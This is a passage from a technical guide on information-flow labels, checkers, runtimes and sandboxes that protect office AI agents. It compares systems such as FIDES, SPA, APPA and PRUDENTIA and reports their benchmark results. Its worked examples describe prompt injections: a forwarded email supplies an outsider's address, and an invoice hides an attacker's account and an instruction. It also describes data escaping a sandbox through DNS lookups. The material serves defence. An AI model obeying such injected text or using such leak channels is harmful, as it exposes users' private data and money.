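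External commands deserve particular attention in a review. The library's documentation shows a program that requests permission to run `python`, which would let an agent run a script that the Scala compiler has not checked. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific commands, such as `git diff` or the build tool `sbt`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical. Even `sbt` runs build scripts from the project's folder, so an agent with permission to use it must not be able to edit those scripts.

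A reviewer also has to check the tool wrappers by reading the signature of every tool, because knowing that a system uses `Classified` isn't enough to tell which data it protects. In the travel interface for the AgentDojo tests, hotel reviews are wrapped in `Classified`, but the user's passport and credit card numbers are returned as plain text and can enter the agent's context. The interface apparently uses `Classified` to keep untrusted text from the agent, not to keep private data secret.

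ACE depends on a similar list, with its own checker and runtime in place of the Scala compiler and library. It also assumes that code can't escape its containers, since Li and colleagues leave such escapes out of scope. The user must label every source of information, including the request. If the user forgets a label, the checker won't detect leaks from that source.

### What the checker gets to see

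Checking a program requires the generated code, the types or labels, and the policies, but not the emails. The office can run the checker on its own machine, or show the program to an outside reviewer without showing any client's correspondence. Some private information may still be visible, because the code can contain names or figures the user typed into the request, and reader sets show who is working with whom.

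An outside service that audits an agent's individual calls needs to see much more. *When Safety Checks Become Privacy Risks* (Luo, Ma and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an office agent that may read internal pricing documents but is told to send a customer only the public version of a quotation. To judge whether a proposed email is allowed, the auditor needs the user's instructions, the recipient, the text and its source. The auditor then learns the company's internal costs and the customer's identity, even if it blocks the email. Luo and colleagues call this "audit-induced privacy exposure".

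SealCall lets the auditor check a proposed call without reading the user's data. Software under the user's control turns the task, the proposed call and the relevant history into a list of numbers and encrypts it. The auditor holds encrypted examples of unsafe calls and computes how similar the proposed call is to each one, using homomorphic encryption, which permits arithmetic on encrypted numbers. The user's software decrypts the scores and blocks the call if the highest one passes a threshold. One similarity calculation took 0.176 seconds on average in a typical configuration.

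Encryption protects the content from an auditor that follows the protocol but tries to infer private information. The judgement can still be wrong. On 1,252 proposed calls, SealCall reached a mean F1 score of 0.840, where 1 is perfect. F1 combines the share of flagged calls that were unsafe with the share of unsafe calls that the system flagged. A label check enforces its rule without such errors, but it can still accept a leak if the labels are wrong.

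The quotation example doesn't need an auditor if the company has labelled the internal price list and the public quotation separately. The program names the document it sends, and the checker compares that document's label with the recipient. An auditor becomes useful when the agent has to write the public quotation from the internal price list. The quotation then inherits the price list's strict label, and somebody has to read the text to decide whether it is fit to send.

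## Enforcing the rules while the program runs

The Project X program may send its summary only if the manager is allowed to read every email used in it. A checker that examines the program before it runs can't know which emails the search will find, so it has to assume that the manager isn't allowed to read some of them. The runtime can wait until the emails arrive, work out the summary's label, and stop the sending call if the manager isn't among the permitted readers.

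### What only a run can settle

Recipients often depend on data. Microsoft gives the example of an agent that posts a message to a channel in Teams, the company's chat service. The call names the channel, but the people who will read the message are whoever belongs to the channel at that moment. Microsoft's policy for the posting tool works as follows:

1. If the agent chose the call in a trusted context, the policy allows it.
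2. Otherwise, the policy fetches the list of members and allows the call if all of them may read the text.
3. If some of them may not, the user has to decide, and the request for approval lists the people who would newly see the text.

This order suits an agent in a loop, whose context becomes untrusted as it reads untrusted data. In a generated program, the planning model chooses every call before reading anything untrusted, so step 1 would allow every message and the list of members would never matter. An office that wants the membership check has to remove step 1.

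A label may also be unknown until a tool opens the data. In an example from Microsoft's May announcement of FIDES, a tool fetches a bug report from GitHub and labels it public or private to match the repository. The same line of code can produce either label, and the repository's owner can change the setting after a checker has approved the program.

Some systems produce code in stages. A checker can examine each program just before it runs, but a later program may use values that an earlier one left behind. The runtime holds those values, so it has to keep their labels and supply them to the checker.

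### The labelled loop in FIDES, line by line

Costa and colleagues add labels to the tool-calling loop in an algorithm of about a dozen lines. In simplified notation:

```
 1  loop(state, store, message):
 2      action = planner(state, message)
 3      if action is "ask the model" with history h and tool list t:
 4          reply = model(h, t)
 5          label(reply) = label(h) ⊔ label(t)
 6          continue the loop with reply
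 7      if action is "call tool f" with arguments a1 ... an:
 8          if the policy forbids the call: stop
 9          result = f(store, a1 ... an)
10          new = label(call) ⊔ label(a1) ⊔ ... ⊔ label(an)
11                ⊔ label(everything in the store that f may read)
12          label(result) = new
13          label(everything in the store that f may write) = new
14          continue the loop with result
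15      if action is "finish" with answer r:
16          return r and its label
```

Line 1 has three inputs. The state contains the conversation so far and any values hidden from the model. The store is all the data that tools can reach, such as the mailbox and the calendar, with a label on each item. The message is the latest in the conversation and also has a label.

On line 2, the planner, which is conventional software surrounding the language model, turns the message into one of three actions. It also replaces the names of hidden values with the labelled values, so an email's recipient and body can reach line 7 with different labels.

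Lines 3 to 6 handle a call to the model. The reply gets the joined label of everything the model received, including the tool list, which FIDES labels trusted and public. A deployer who uses tool descriptions from outside suppliers could label the list untrusted, but then every tool call the model chose would also be untrusted.

Line 8 of the algorithm checks whether the call is allowed before the tool runs, and a forbidden call ends the run. In Costa and colleagues' experiments, the software instead reported the refusal to the model and continued.

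Lines 9 to 12 run the tool and label its result. New labels enter on line 11. When `read_emails` fetches Ben's message, for example, the message's label comes from the store. The label of the call also affects the result's label, because an outsider who gets the agent to search for a particular word influences what the search returns. Taken literally, line 11 would give every search result the joined label of the whole mailbox, since the tool may read any of it. The FIDES tests avoid this by labelling the items that a tool actually returns.

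Line 13 covers data that a tool saves. If a program writes the summary to a shared folder, the file gets the summary's label, so a program that opens the file next week will receive the untrusted text with the correct label. Writing to a file replaces its old label, so the developer of a tool that adds text to a file must list that file as something the tool reads. Otherwise, after the tool adds one trusted sentence, the whole file would be labeled trusted.

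Line 16 returns the answer with its label, so the application can warn the user that an answer draws on untrusted text.

The same rules work for a generated program, whose lines replace the planner's decisions. The runtime applies lines 7 to 14 to each tool call and labels the isolated model's output as on line 5. It also joins labels when the program itself combines two values, such as by adding numbers or concatenating text.

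Costa and colleagues treat questions to the model and answers to the user as harmless, so their loop tests only tool calls. They note that the test can move to just after line 2, where it covers every action. An office that restricts which provider may read its mail needs this broader test, because a question to a hosted model also sends data out. The loop can also keep a record of earlier calls for policies to use. With that record, enforcing a limit of three messages per run, which an ordinary type checker can't verify, requires only a counter.

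None of this works unless tool results have labels. Microsoft sends them in a metadata field that MCP already has, so software that doesn't understand labels can still use the tools. GitHub's MCP server can now label files from public repositories as public and untrusted, and files from private ones as private and trusted. Microsoft also published a gateway that adds labels to the results of other servers, although somebody has to write a labelling function for each tool. For the remaining tools, software can infer cautious labels by assuming that every argument flows into the result, that results from the open web are untrusted, and that anything behind a login is private.

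### Two runs of the Project X program

Suppose the search finds only the emails from Ana and Ben, and the isolated model runs on the office's own machine. The `send_email` policy has separate limits. The call and the recipient must be trusted, and everyone who receives the body must be among its allowed readers.

In the honest run, the program takes the manager's address from the user's settings. In the other run, the planning model has written a program that looks for the address in the mail:

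```
address = isolated_model("Who should receive progress reports?", emails)
send_email(to=address, body=summary)
```

Ben has forwarded a note that gives an outsider's address for this purpose. The runtime produces these labels and verdicts:

| Run | Step | Value | Readers | Trust | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Both | Read the mail | `emails` | User, manager | Untrusted | Allowed: the call and the search term are trusted |
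| Both | Summarise | `summary` | User, manager | Untrusted | Allowed: the text stays in the office |
| Honest | Send | `summary`, to `manager` | User, manager | Call and recipient trusted, body untrusted | Allowed: the manager may read the body |
| Changed | Find the recipient | `address` | User, manager | Untrusted | Allowed: the text stays in the office |
| Changed | Send | `summary`, to `address` | User, manager | Call trusted, recipient and body untrusted | Stopped: the recipient is untrusted, and the outsider may not read the body |

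The changed run breaks two limits. The limit on the recipient's integrity would stop the call even if Ben's email had contained the manager's real address, because the policy compares labels and doesn't check the address itself. If the user had instead pasted an injection into the request, and the planning model had then written the outsider's address directly into the program, the call and the address would both have the label "trusted", and only the limit on readers would protect the emails.

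A checker could have rejected the changed program before it ran, because that program takes `address` from an email, whatever the email says. To approve the original program, the checker would have needed to know which emails the search would find.

### When one email marks everything

The conservative rule on line 5 makes labels stricter with every step. *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, by Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), calls this problem by its established name, "label creep". Microsoft acknowledges the problem in its own product. Once an untrusted bug report enters the context, the rest of the run is untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes the report.

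Microsoft describes a case where the rule works as intended. Alex asks an agent to reply to his unanswered emails. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't supposed to see the figures yet, has asked about them. Once the agent has read both emails, only Alex may read anything it writes, so it can't send Marco a reply without approval. But the same rule stops a reply that tells Marco only that Alex will be in touch next week, because the label depends on what the model has read, and a harmless sentence gets the same label as the sales figures.

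Costa and colleagues measured how policy checks affect the share of AgentDojo tasks completed. With GPT-4o and no attack, an ordinary loop completed 75.0% of office tasks without the checks and 37.0% with them. In the chat tasks, the share fell from 93.3% to 20.0%. The checks didn't lower the share for travel tasks, because many of the tools they need may run in an untrusted context as long as no confidential data gets out. With o1, a stronger model, the ordinary loop's share of chat tasks still fell from 87.6% to 17.1%. Hiding untrusted results from the planning model, as FIDES does, reduced the loss. With GPT-4o, the checks lowered FIDES's share from 63.5% to 59.0% in the office tasks and from 63.8% to 47.6% in the chat tasks.

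Hiding data protects the planning model's context, but the isolated model still has to read the emails, and its answer still gets all their labels. Siddiqui and colleagues try to give such an answer only the labels of the documents that influenced it. Their method has four steps:

1. The model answers the question from all the documents.
2. The software takes a less restrictive label and removes every document above it. It then measures how likely the model would be to produce the same answer from the remaining documents.
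3. If the answer is almost as likely as before, the software accepts the smaller set and tries to reduce it further.
4. The model answers the question again from the smaller set alone. The user receives this new answer, with the label of the smaller set.

The measure in step 2 is perplexity, which is low when the model gives a text a high probability. The software accepts a label L′ if the perplexity rises by no more than a chosen tolerance λ:

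```
perplexity(answer | documents at or below L′)
    − perplexity(answer | all documents)  ≤  λ
```

In one example, a user asks how many people live in New York City. A trusted web page gives 8.4 million and an untrusted one about 8 million. The model can produce its answer of 8.4 million from the trusted page alone, so the answer can be labeled "trusted".

Step 4 makes the method safe because the model call that produces the final answer never receives the removed documents. The estimate of influence can be wrong, and a hostile document can distort it, but this lowers the answer's quality without making its label incorrect.

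Siddiqui and colleagues tested the method on 40 short agent conversations, 20 of which could have been given a less restrictive label. The method found that label in 17 cases with the smaller of two Llama-2 models and in 19 with the larger. Asking the model which documents it had used found the label in 9 cases with the smaller model and 16 with the larger. On a larger set of questions about news articles, the method improved 57% of the improvable labels when using the smaller model and 39% when using the larger. In roughly a fifth of those improvements, it had dropped an article that the answer needed. These results show that the idea can work, but Llama-2 dates from 2023 and the agent conversations were few and simple, so we can't tell from them how often it would work in an office today.

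The method also needs extra model calls. With two labels it has to try only one smaller set, but in the worst case the number of sets to try grows exponentially with the number of documents. An attacker can also block the improvement by adding distracting documents until the model no longer gives the same answer without them.

A generated program can often avoid the search. Siddiqui and colleagues point out that if the required label is known in advance, the software can leave out every document above it. The Project X program specifies its recipient before the isolated model reads anything. The runtime could therefore remove any email the manager is not allowed to read, such as a stray one from an outsider, and summarise the rest. It should notify the user of any omissions, because the summary alone would not reveal them.

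A later method, *GIF* (2026), measures influence inside the model. It calculates how much a small change to each part of the input would change the output, and uses the result to set an upper limit on how much information could have passed. In one example, an address in a user's private notes has no effect on the output. *GIF* assigns it a flow of zero, while a measure based on the model's attention (the weights it gives to different parts of its input) attributes 9% to it. *GIF*'s guarantee holds only near the actual input, and the calculation requires access to the model's internals, which customers of a hosted model don't normally have. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* still describes tracking labels through language models as an open problem, so a builder who needs a firm guarantee should join all the input labels or generate the answer again from fewer documents.

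### Checks before the run and during it

A check before the run reasons about everything a program could do, and a check during the run deals with what it is doing now. This leads to different strengths:

| | Before the run | During the run |
|---|---|---|
| Paths through the program | All of them, including branches that never run | Only the one the program takes |
| Labels | The strictest that each tool might return | Those of the data that arrived |
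| Recipients | Those fixed in the program or the settings | All of them, including computed ones |
| Effects of a refusal | No tool has run | Earlier calls may already have had effects |
| Main cost | Rejects programs that would have been safe | Tests every call, and every call has to go through the runtime |

Stopping a program at runtime can leave its task partly done, which matters most when the program sends several messages. Suppose the program that announces a vacation to all regular collaborators tries to send its seventh message to an address it isn't allowed to use. The runtime can stop that message, but the first six have already been sent. If the program also cancels meetings, it may stop with only some of them cancelled.

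For this reason, Girrens and Wang designed SPA to finish all its checks before the program runs. If any check fails, SPA ends the request without running any tools. It calls the planning model only once per request and doesn't send it the reasons a plan failed, because a model that received them could keep changing an unsafe plan until it passed. The disadvantage is that an ordinary mistake in the plan also ends the request.

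A check before the run, such as ACE's, can also cover information that a program reveals through its choice of branch, whereas the labelled loop tracks only data that the program copies into its calls. But a check before the run must use baseline labels, so it rejects the legitimate Project X program if the mailbox might contain anything the manager isn't allowed to read.

The runtime avoids that false refusal, but it can test only the calls that pass through it, which is why FIDES doesn't protect generated programs in Microsoft's package. A checker that examines the program's text doesn't have this weakness, but someone still has to ensure that the runtime executes exactly the program the checker approved.

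An office assistant should probably check programs both before and while they run. The checker can sort programs into three groups: those that always break a rule, those that never can, and those that might, depending on the data. It rejects the first group. For the Project X program, it can confirm that the planning model chose the sending call and that the recipient comes from the settings. It leaves one condition to the runtime, which checks whether the manager is one of the summary's actual readers. Both checks should use the same policy file, so that any rule change applies to both.

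Using both also helps with programs that stop halfway. If a program's reading and sending steps are separate, the runtime can finish reading, work out every message's recipient and body, and test all the messages before it sends any. This works for the vacation announcement, but not for a program that must send a question and wait for the reply before choosing its next step.

### What the sandbox adds

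A policy for `send_email` can stop a message only if the message goes through `send_email`. Code in a general-purpose language may be able to send it another way, such as through a network library or an outside command. Even a strict compiler like TACIT's can't examine what an outside command does, so a sandbox has to contain it.

NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* explains why the operating system has to enforce these limits. An application can inspect a tool call and its arguments before the call runs, but once the call starts another program, the application can no longer see or control what that program does. Attackers often use an approved tool to reach a forbidden one. Limits set by the operating system apply to every program inside the sandbox, however it started.

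NVIDIA's security team wrote its advice for coding agents and considers three limits mandatory:

- Code in the sandbox can't connect to the network, except to approved addresses. This stops it from sending data out or giving an attacker remote access.
- It can't write files outside its working folder. Some files elsewhere run automatically when the user opens a terminal, so a program that changed one could run code outside the sandbox later.
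- It can't change the agent's own configuration files, even inside the working folder. These files can contain commands that the agent runs outside the sandbox, so NVIDIA wants users to edit them by hand and not to approve such changes through the agent.

The team also recommends a separate virtual machine. Containers normally share the host machine's kernel, so a kernel fault may let code escape, and ACE's security claims assume it can't.

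The simplest way to enforce the rules on a generated program is to run it in a sandbox with no network access and a single connection to the runtime. The program sends each tool call request to the runtime, which checks the labels and makes the call from outside the sandbox. Passwords and access keys can stay with the runtime, so the sandbox contains none for the code to steal.

The sandbox can't replace the label checks, because it doesn't track what the data is or who may read it. If the program connects directly to a mail server, the sandbox has to permit that connection, and messages to the manager and to an outsider may both go through it. The label checks also depend on the sandbox having no other way out. In March 2026, Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Flaw in AWS Bedrock Code Interpreter Raises Alarms* reported that researchers had got data out of an Amazon cloud sandbox that showed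 its network access as disabled. The data left through the system that looks up internet addresses by name, which NVIDIA advises restricting to a few trusted servers. According to the article, Amazon called this channel intended behaviour and changed its documentation instead of issuing a patch. A deployer should therefore test what can leave a sandbox before relying on a setting meant to isolate it.

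## Handling refusals, approvals and later requests

A refusal protects the data but leaves the user without the message or payment they asked for. The system can then return the error to the planning model for a rewrite, look for a plan that exposes less data, ask a person, or stop. SPA always stops, which is the safest choice, but users may switch off the checks if the assistant gives up on too many legitimate tasks.

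### Returning the error for a rewrite

A rewrite works best when the program failed because of a coding mistake. TACIT sends compiler errors back to the model. In Odersky and colleagues' tests on τ²-bench, between 0.32% and 7.93% of the generated programs needed a retry, depending on the model and the type of task, and the model then usually succeeded within one or two attempts. Recurring errors included mishandled null values and missing escape characters, which are unrelated to protected data.

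Like these compiler errors, a refusal before the run contains little that the planning model doesn't already know. A refusal during the run depends on the real data, and the message can reveal some of it:

| Information in the error | Show it to the planning model? |
|---|---|
| Line number, expected type and actual type | Yes. They come from the program and the tool descriptions. |
| Name of the rule and of the argument that broke it | Usually. During a run, they also reveal one fact about the data. |
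| Names of the people who may read the data | No, unless the model already has them. They show who corresponds with whom. |
| An address or other value that the program computed | No. An outsider may have written it. |
| The tool's own error text | No. It may quote an email. |

A refusal itself gives the model information. If the runtime won't send the Project X summary to the manager, the model can infer that the search found an email the manager may not read. Trying one recipient after another could reveal more, so the runtime should limit the number of attempts. An outsider can also cause a refusal by sending a stray email, and so gain some influence over the rewrite.

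Using a fixed message keeps a hostile email's influence small, because the email can trigger the message but can't change its wording. In the system from Kolluri and colleagues, for example, the isolated model uses a fixed message to request more information.

Girrens and Wang don't let a model retry, but retries are a risk only if the check has gaps. If someone has mislabelled a folder or forgotten a policy, for example, each retry gives a manipulated planning model another chance to find the mistake.

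### Finding a route that exposes less

Even when the code is sound, a system may refuse a request for other reasons, such as when the agent has already read something that its next message must not reveal. *APPA* (Agentic Permissions Policy Algebra; Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that answers such a refusal with a list of permitted ways to proceed. It works with an ordinary tool-calling agent, but a runtime for generated programs could offer similar options.

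APPA checks each call twice. Before the call, it works out the label that the agent's context would have afterwards:

```
label after the call = current label, combined with the label
                       that the tool declares for its result
```

Some tools read and send data in a single step. One test tool, for example, reads a confidential finance document and emails it to outside lawyers. APPA stops this call before the tool reads the file, because its check includes the document's label. A check that used only the current label would allow the call, since the agent hasn't read anything confidential yet. After a permitted call, APPA checks the actual result before letting it into the context, in case the tool returned something other than what it declared.

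When a check fails, reading more data can't help if the problem is who may receive the text or how far the system trusts it. Every reading step leaves the label as it is or makes it stricter. Kravchenko and colleagues prove this, and they list four kinds of step that can help:

- The agent completes a prerequisite. In one test, it has to log a clearance before it sends contract terms to a client.
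- An authority approves this one call. The authority can be a fixed rule, a person or a second language model, and the deployer sets limits on what each may approve.
- Approved software transforms the data, for example by removing personal details, or works out a missing label.
- The agent performs the reading step in a temporary branch, so that the main context never receives the data.

The agent can also accept the stricter label and give up the actions it forbids. Suppose the agent has to read an internal customer ticket and then file a public bug report. If the ticket enters the main context, the agent can no longer publish anything without approval. Before this happens, APPA offers alternatives, such as reading the ticket in a branch or passing it through a redaction tool.

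The deployer registers every route in advance, so the software can search them all and either return one that works or report that none does. It can't find routes outside this list. For example, if an administrator has just widened access to a folder, the search won't account for it.

A branch starts with a copy of the conversation and its label. The agent specifies a fixed form for the answer before the branch reads anything, to protect the main context. For example, a branch that reads a public bug report might return a ticket number, a severity and a component from a list. As with the isolated model's fixed-form answers, a hostile report can still make the branch choose a false value, so the deployer has to decide whether to trust the answer. Unlike the isolated model, a branch can also call tools, and discarding the branch doesn't undo what those tools did.

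#### How much recovery helped

Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA with GPT-5.6 Luna, DeepSeek V4 Flash and Gemini 3.7 Flash on Bench-Corp, their own benchmark of 20 simulated office scenarios. Many of the scenarios require another action after the agent has read restricted data. Each model ran each scenario five times with a normal prompt and five times with one that encouraged it to follow instructions hidden in the data. Software scored each run by checking the files and messages left at the end, without using a language model as judge.

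APPA completed between 87% and 91% of the tasks, and none of the attacks succeeded in 600 runs. For Luna, they also removed parts of the recovery system:

| Version, with GPT-5.6 Luna | Tasks completed | Runs with a successful attack |
|---|---|---|
| Restrictions lifted | 90.5% | 33% |
| Full APPA | 88.0% | 0% |
| No branches | 56.5% | 0% |
| No list of routes after a refusal | 35.0% | 0% |

Each row covers 200 runs. All three restricted versions stopped the attacks, so recovery accounts for the difference in completed tasks. However, Kravchenko and colleagues designed the scenarios to exercise APPA's own mechanisms, so the 88% is weak evidence about an office with other kinds of work.

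Kravchenko and colleagues' comparison with FIDES needs similar caution. Two FIDES configurations completed between 36% and 46% of the Bench-Corp tasks, and attacks succeeded in 26% to 35% of runs. But the researchers wrote the policies for both configurations, and those policies didn't cover several of the benchmark's rules, such as exact recipients and required prior steps, so the results don't show the best that FIDES could do.

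The evidence from AgentThreatBench is more independent, because other people wrote its 24 tasks. APPA completed between 64.2% and 76.7% of them, and again no attack succeeded in any of the 720 runs. With DeepSeek, both FIDES configurations completed more tasks than APPA, but attacks succeeded in 30.0% and 25.0% of their runs when the prompt encouraged the model to obey hidden instructions. APPA did worst on tasks about poisoned memory, where many of its failures were correct answers that lacked the exact phrase the scorer required.

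In a smaller test, the agent had to deliver 30 messages to authorised recipients and withhold 30 others. APPA delivered 24 of the permitted messages and withheld all the forbidden ones. Both FIDES configurations withheld all 60 messages because their policies didn't link each record to the people allowed to receive it.

### Measuring how often the agent needs a person

Kolluri and colleagues argue that earlier studies compared protected and unprotected agents unfairly. The studies counted a protected agent's task as failed if a policy blocked a call, but let the unprotected agent act without asking the user. In practice, many unprotected agents do stop to ask. GitHub Copilot Chat in Visual Studio Code, for example, requires the user to approve any tool call that does more than read. A label check could remove many of these requests, because the agent would only have to ask about calls that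 fail the check.

They propose two measures of this benefit. For each run, let v be the number of tool calls that break a policy and so require approval:

```
HITL load = total of v over all successfully completed tasks
TCR@k     = share of all tasks completed with v ≤ k
```

HITL stands for "human in the loop", and TCR for "task completion rate". The HITL load is the number of approvals an agent needs across the tasks it completes. TCR@0 is the share of all tasks it completes without asking for approval, and TCR@1 is the share it completes with at most one approval. An agent that completes three tasks with 0, 1 and 4 approvals, and fails a fourth, has a load of 5, a TCR@0 of 25% and a TCR@1 of 50%. The load excludes failed tasks, so an agent can also reduce it by completing fewer tasks.

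The agent PRUDENTIA adds a planner to FIDES that tries to avoid policy violations. The tool descriptions state each tool's policy, and the planning model is told whether its context is still trusted. Before opening hidden data, it must state why it needs to read the data and which calls it expects to make afterwards. The label checks run outside the model, so a bad plan can lead to more questions or a failed task but can't cause a forbidden call.

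PRUDENTIA can also choose whether to ask the user to approve individual calls or to endorse the data as trusted. Suppose an email contains ten jobs, each requiring a consequential call. If the agent reads the email without endorsement, its context becomes untrusted and the user has to approve all ten calls, whereas endorsing the email takes only one question. The instructions tell the model to request endorsement if it expects more than one consequential call, and otherwise to read the email and leave any approval until later.

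Kolluri and colleagues ran each agent five times on AgentDojo. The basic agent asks before every consequential call, while the others ask only when a label check fails. Each cell gives the HITL load, followed by TCR@0:

| Agent | GPT-4o | o4-mini | GPT-5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | 59.4 / 28.0% | 48.6 / 32.8% | 52.0 / 35.1% |
| Basic with label checks | 39.4 / 38.4% | 34.6 / 42.5% | 40.4 / 43.4% |
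| FIDES | 7.8 / 50.3% | 36.8 / 53.2% | 41.3 / 57.1% |
| PRUDENTIA | 23.8 / 42.5% | 19.2 / 59.4% | 7.3 / 72.7% |

With GPT-5, PRUDENTIA needed less than a fifth as many approvals as FIDES and completed about as many tasks overall. With GPT-4o, it did worse than FIDES on both measures. Planning around policies seems to require a model that reasons well, so a team with a weaker model may do better with plain FIDES. The planning also requires long instructions and extra turns. With GPT-4o, an average office task cost 3.9 US cents with PRUDENTIA and 1.7 cents with FIDES.

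On WASP, a benchmark of simulated websites, PRUDENTIA needed no approvals, while the basic agent needed between 1.0 and 3.7 per task. The user's tasks were only to comment on a post or upvote it, so the agent never had to read what strangers had written.

In these experiments, Kolluri and colleagues counted how often an agent would ask the user for approval. They didn't have people answer the requests, but assumed that the user would approve legitimate calls and stop attacks. The results therefore don't show how well a real person would decide.

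### Making approval mean something

People who see too many approval requests stop reading them. Kolluri and colleagues call this "confirmation fatigue" and cite earlier work on security prompts and on alerts in medical software. Fewer approval requests should help, but the label checks can't replace all of them. A call that satisfies every policy may still come from a misread instruction, and an office may need a person's consent for legal reasons.

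Asking fewer questions can also make each one harder to answer. If the user approves ten calls separately, an eleventh that an attacker added to the list gets its own question. If the user endorses the whole email, they have to spot the extra line themselves, and every call that follows from the email then counts as trusted. Endorsement therefore suits a short text from a known sender. For a long document, the system should ask about individual calls or extract a few values for the user to confirm.

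An attacker may try to control what the approval screen displays. Kolluri and colleagues leave its design to future work but suggest showing the labels and the origin of the data, since attackers can't change the labels. A useful request for approval should contain at least the following:

- The exact action, with the recipient's full address and the complete text.
- The source of each argument, such as the user's settings or a stranger's email.
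- The rule that failed, in ordinary words.
- What would change if the person agreed, including who could newly read the data.

The runtime should fill in these details itself, because a manipulated model could describe a payment to a stranger as a routine refund. The screen should clearly label any explanation from a model and place it below these details. It should show protected text only to someone allowed to read it, and must not send that text back to the planning model.

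The approval also has to apply to the call the person saw. In APPA, an approval covers one call with exactly those arguments and expires when the call runs. It doesn't change any labels, so sending the same document again requires a new decision. The limits on each authority also matter, because a user who may approve a calendar invitation shouldn't automatically be able to release a colleague's personnel file. If no one with the necessary authority is available, the system should stop.

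### Why the second request is harder

The planning model starts the first request with a clean context. By the second request, an ordinary agent's context may contain the emails it fetched, the summary it wrote and any instructions an outsider hid in them. The user may refer to "that summary" or "the invoice from yesterday", so the planner must be told which earlier results exist. If it reads those results, it loses the protection of a clean context.

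In Girrens and Wang's example, an invoice contains the attacker's bank account and a malicious instruction. On Monday, the user asks the agent to fetch the invoice and keep its details. The attack has no effect until Tuesday, when the user asks the agent to pay the invoice. The instruction can then affect the plan, or a correct plan can send the money to the attacker's account.

SPA prevents both by storing each result in three parts. The runtime keeps the value and its label. The planning model receives only a description of the result's form, its purpose and meaning, and the request that produced it. The planning model wrote the purpose and meaning on Monday before any tool ran, so they contain none of the invoice's text. On Tuesday, it writes a complete new plan that retrieves the invoice by reference, with its original label still attached. If the payment tool requires trusted input,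 the checker rejects the plan.

SPA would also reject payment of a genuine invoice, because the account number still comes from an outside document. It has no approval step that would let such a payment through. Girrens and Wang suggest that future versions could let someone mark a value as more trusted after an explicit check.

To test later requests, they split each of AgentDojo's 97 tasks into two to five requests and called the result AgentDojo-MQ. They placed the attacks in the data once, at the start, and kept the session's state between requests. With GPT-5.4-nano as the planner, the results were:

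| Version of SPA | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Planner sees earlier values, no label checks | 65.9% | 0.6% |
| Planner sees descriptions only, no label checks | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Planner sees descriptions only, with label checks | 35.3% | 0.2% |

Hiding the earlier values caused little disruption. When the necessary result was in storage, later plans retrieved it in 95.4% of cases without label checks and 89.9% with them. Counting cases where no result had reached storage as failures lowers these figures to 80.1% and 73.4%. The label checks were much more disruptive, and about 45% of the runs that used them ended in a refusal.

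The security figures are less informative because attacks almost never succeeded, even when the planner could see earlier values. Girrens and Wang also call their attack a weak test of delayed injection. The case for hiding those values therefore depends more on SPA's design than on this experiment.

### TACIT's two outputs

TACIT keeps a programming session open between requests, so a later program can use variables from an earlier one. If a variable contains a `Classified` value, the value stays wrapped, so the compiler applies the same restrictions. Permissions don't carry over. Each one ends with the block that requested it, so a later program that needs the same folder must request access again.

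When a program prints a result, TACIT sends output to both the user's screen and the planning model. Ordinary text is the same in both, but for a wrapped summary the user sees the real text while the model receives only `Classified(****)`. In an example from Odersky and colleagues, the user then asks about the summary's length. The model writes a program that computes it, and again only the user sees the answer.

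SPA also redacts output, but it hides items from the user's screen, whereas TACIT hides text from the model. If a plan tries to display an item that the screen's policy forbids, SPA replaces it with a marker and shows the rest. TACIT's wrapper carries no list of permitted readers, so an office assistant could combine the two approaches by keeping SPA's labels and descriptions and adding TACIT's separate output for the user.

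### Project X over two requests

Suppose an assistant works this way, and the user asks for the Project X summary as before but also wants to see it:

```
emails  = read_emails(topic="Project X")
summary = isolated_model("Summarise the progress reported here", emails)
send_email(to=manager, body=summary)
show_user(summary)
```

The search finds one email from Ana and one from Ben. The summary appears on the user's screen and goes to the manager. The planning model receives only confirmation that the program finished and that `emails` and `summary` exist. The runtime keeps their values and labels, including the label that lets only the user and the manager read the summary.

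The user then writes, "Send it to Ben as well." The planning model needs one line:

```
send_email(to=ben, body=summary)
```

Ben's address comes from the user's contacts, so the recipient is trusted. The summary already exists, so the checker can use its actual label instead of predicting what a search might return. The checker refuses the program before anything runs because Ben isn't allowed to read Ana's email. The error message gives the line and the rule but doesn't mention Ana.

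The planning model tries a version with fewer sources:

```
allowed = readable_by(emails, ben)
update  = isolated_model("Summarise the progress reported here", allowed)
send_email(to=ben, body=update)
```

Here `readable_by` is a runtime function that keeps only the emails whose labels include Ben. The program satisfies the policy, but the only email left is Ben's own, so the message would tell him what he already knows. The planning model can't notice this because it can't see the emails. The runtime should therefore tell the user that the new version leaves out one of the two emails, and offer to ask for approval of the original message instead:

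```
Send this email?
To:          Ben (address from your contacts)
Text:        the summary you saw earlier [full text]
Sources:     one email from Ana, one email from Ben
Problem:     Ben was not a recipient of Ana's email
If you agree: Ben can read what the summary repeats from it
```

The user can now make an informed decision, perhaps after checking with Ana. If they agree, the runtime sends this text to this address once. The summary's label doesn't change, so a third request to send it to a client would lead to another refusal.

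The user may also refer to the content in a request, such as "The second point looks out of date, so ask Ana about it." The planning model has no access to the second point, but it can pass the user's sentence and `summary` to the isolated model, which drafts the question. The runtime then checks whether Ana may read the draft. If the user instead copies the second point into the request, the text enters the planning model's context and, like the rest of the request, is labeled trusted and public by default.

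## What an approved program can still leak or get wrong

If a checker approves the Project X program, the runtime allows all its calls, and the labels and trusted components are right, then no tool has received data that its policy forbids. The program can still reveal a secret from the protected emails without copying it, because outsiders may be able to infer the secret from the steps the program takes. It can also deliver false or unwanted content while following every rule.

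### Two definitions of a program that doesn't leak

The stricter definition is noninterference, for which Costa and colleagues cite a 1982 paper by Goguen and Meseguer. A program has this property if changing the secret data never changes anything an outsider can see. FIDES provides a weaker property, explicit secrecy, which Schoepe and three co-authors defined in 2016. It considers one path through the program at a time, where a path is the list of steps that remains once every `if` and every loop has gone a particular way. The secret data must not change what an outsider sees of those steps. For a generated program, the two definitions are, in simplified notation:

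```
d1 ~ d2    two states of the data that look the same to an outsider
P(d)       the state after program P has run on d
g(d)       the state after one fixed path through P has run on d

noninterference:    if d1 ~ d2, then P(d1) ~ P(d2)
explicit secrecy:   for every path g that P can take,
                    if d1 ~ d2, then g(d1) ~ g(d2)
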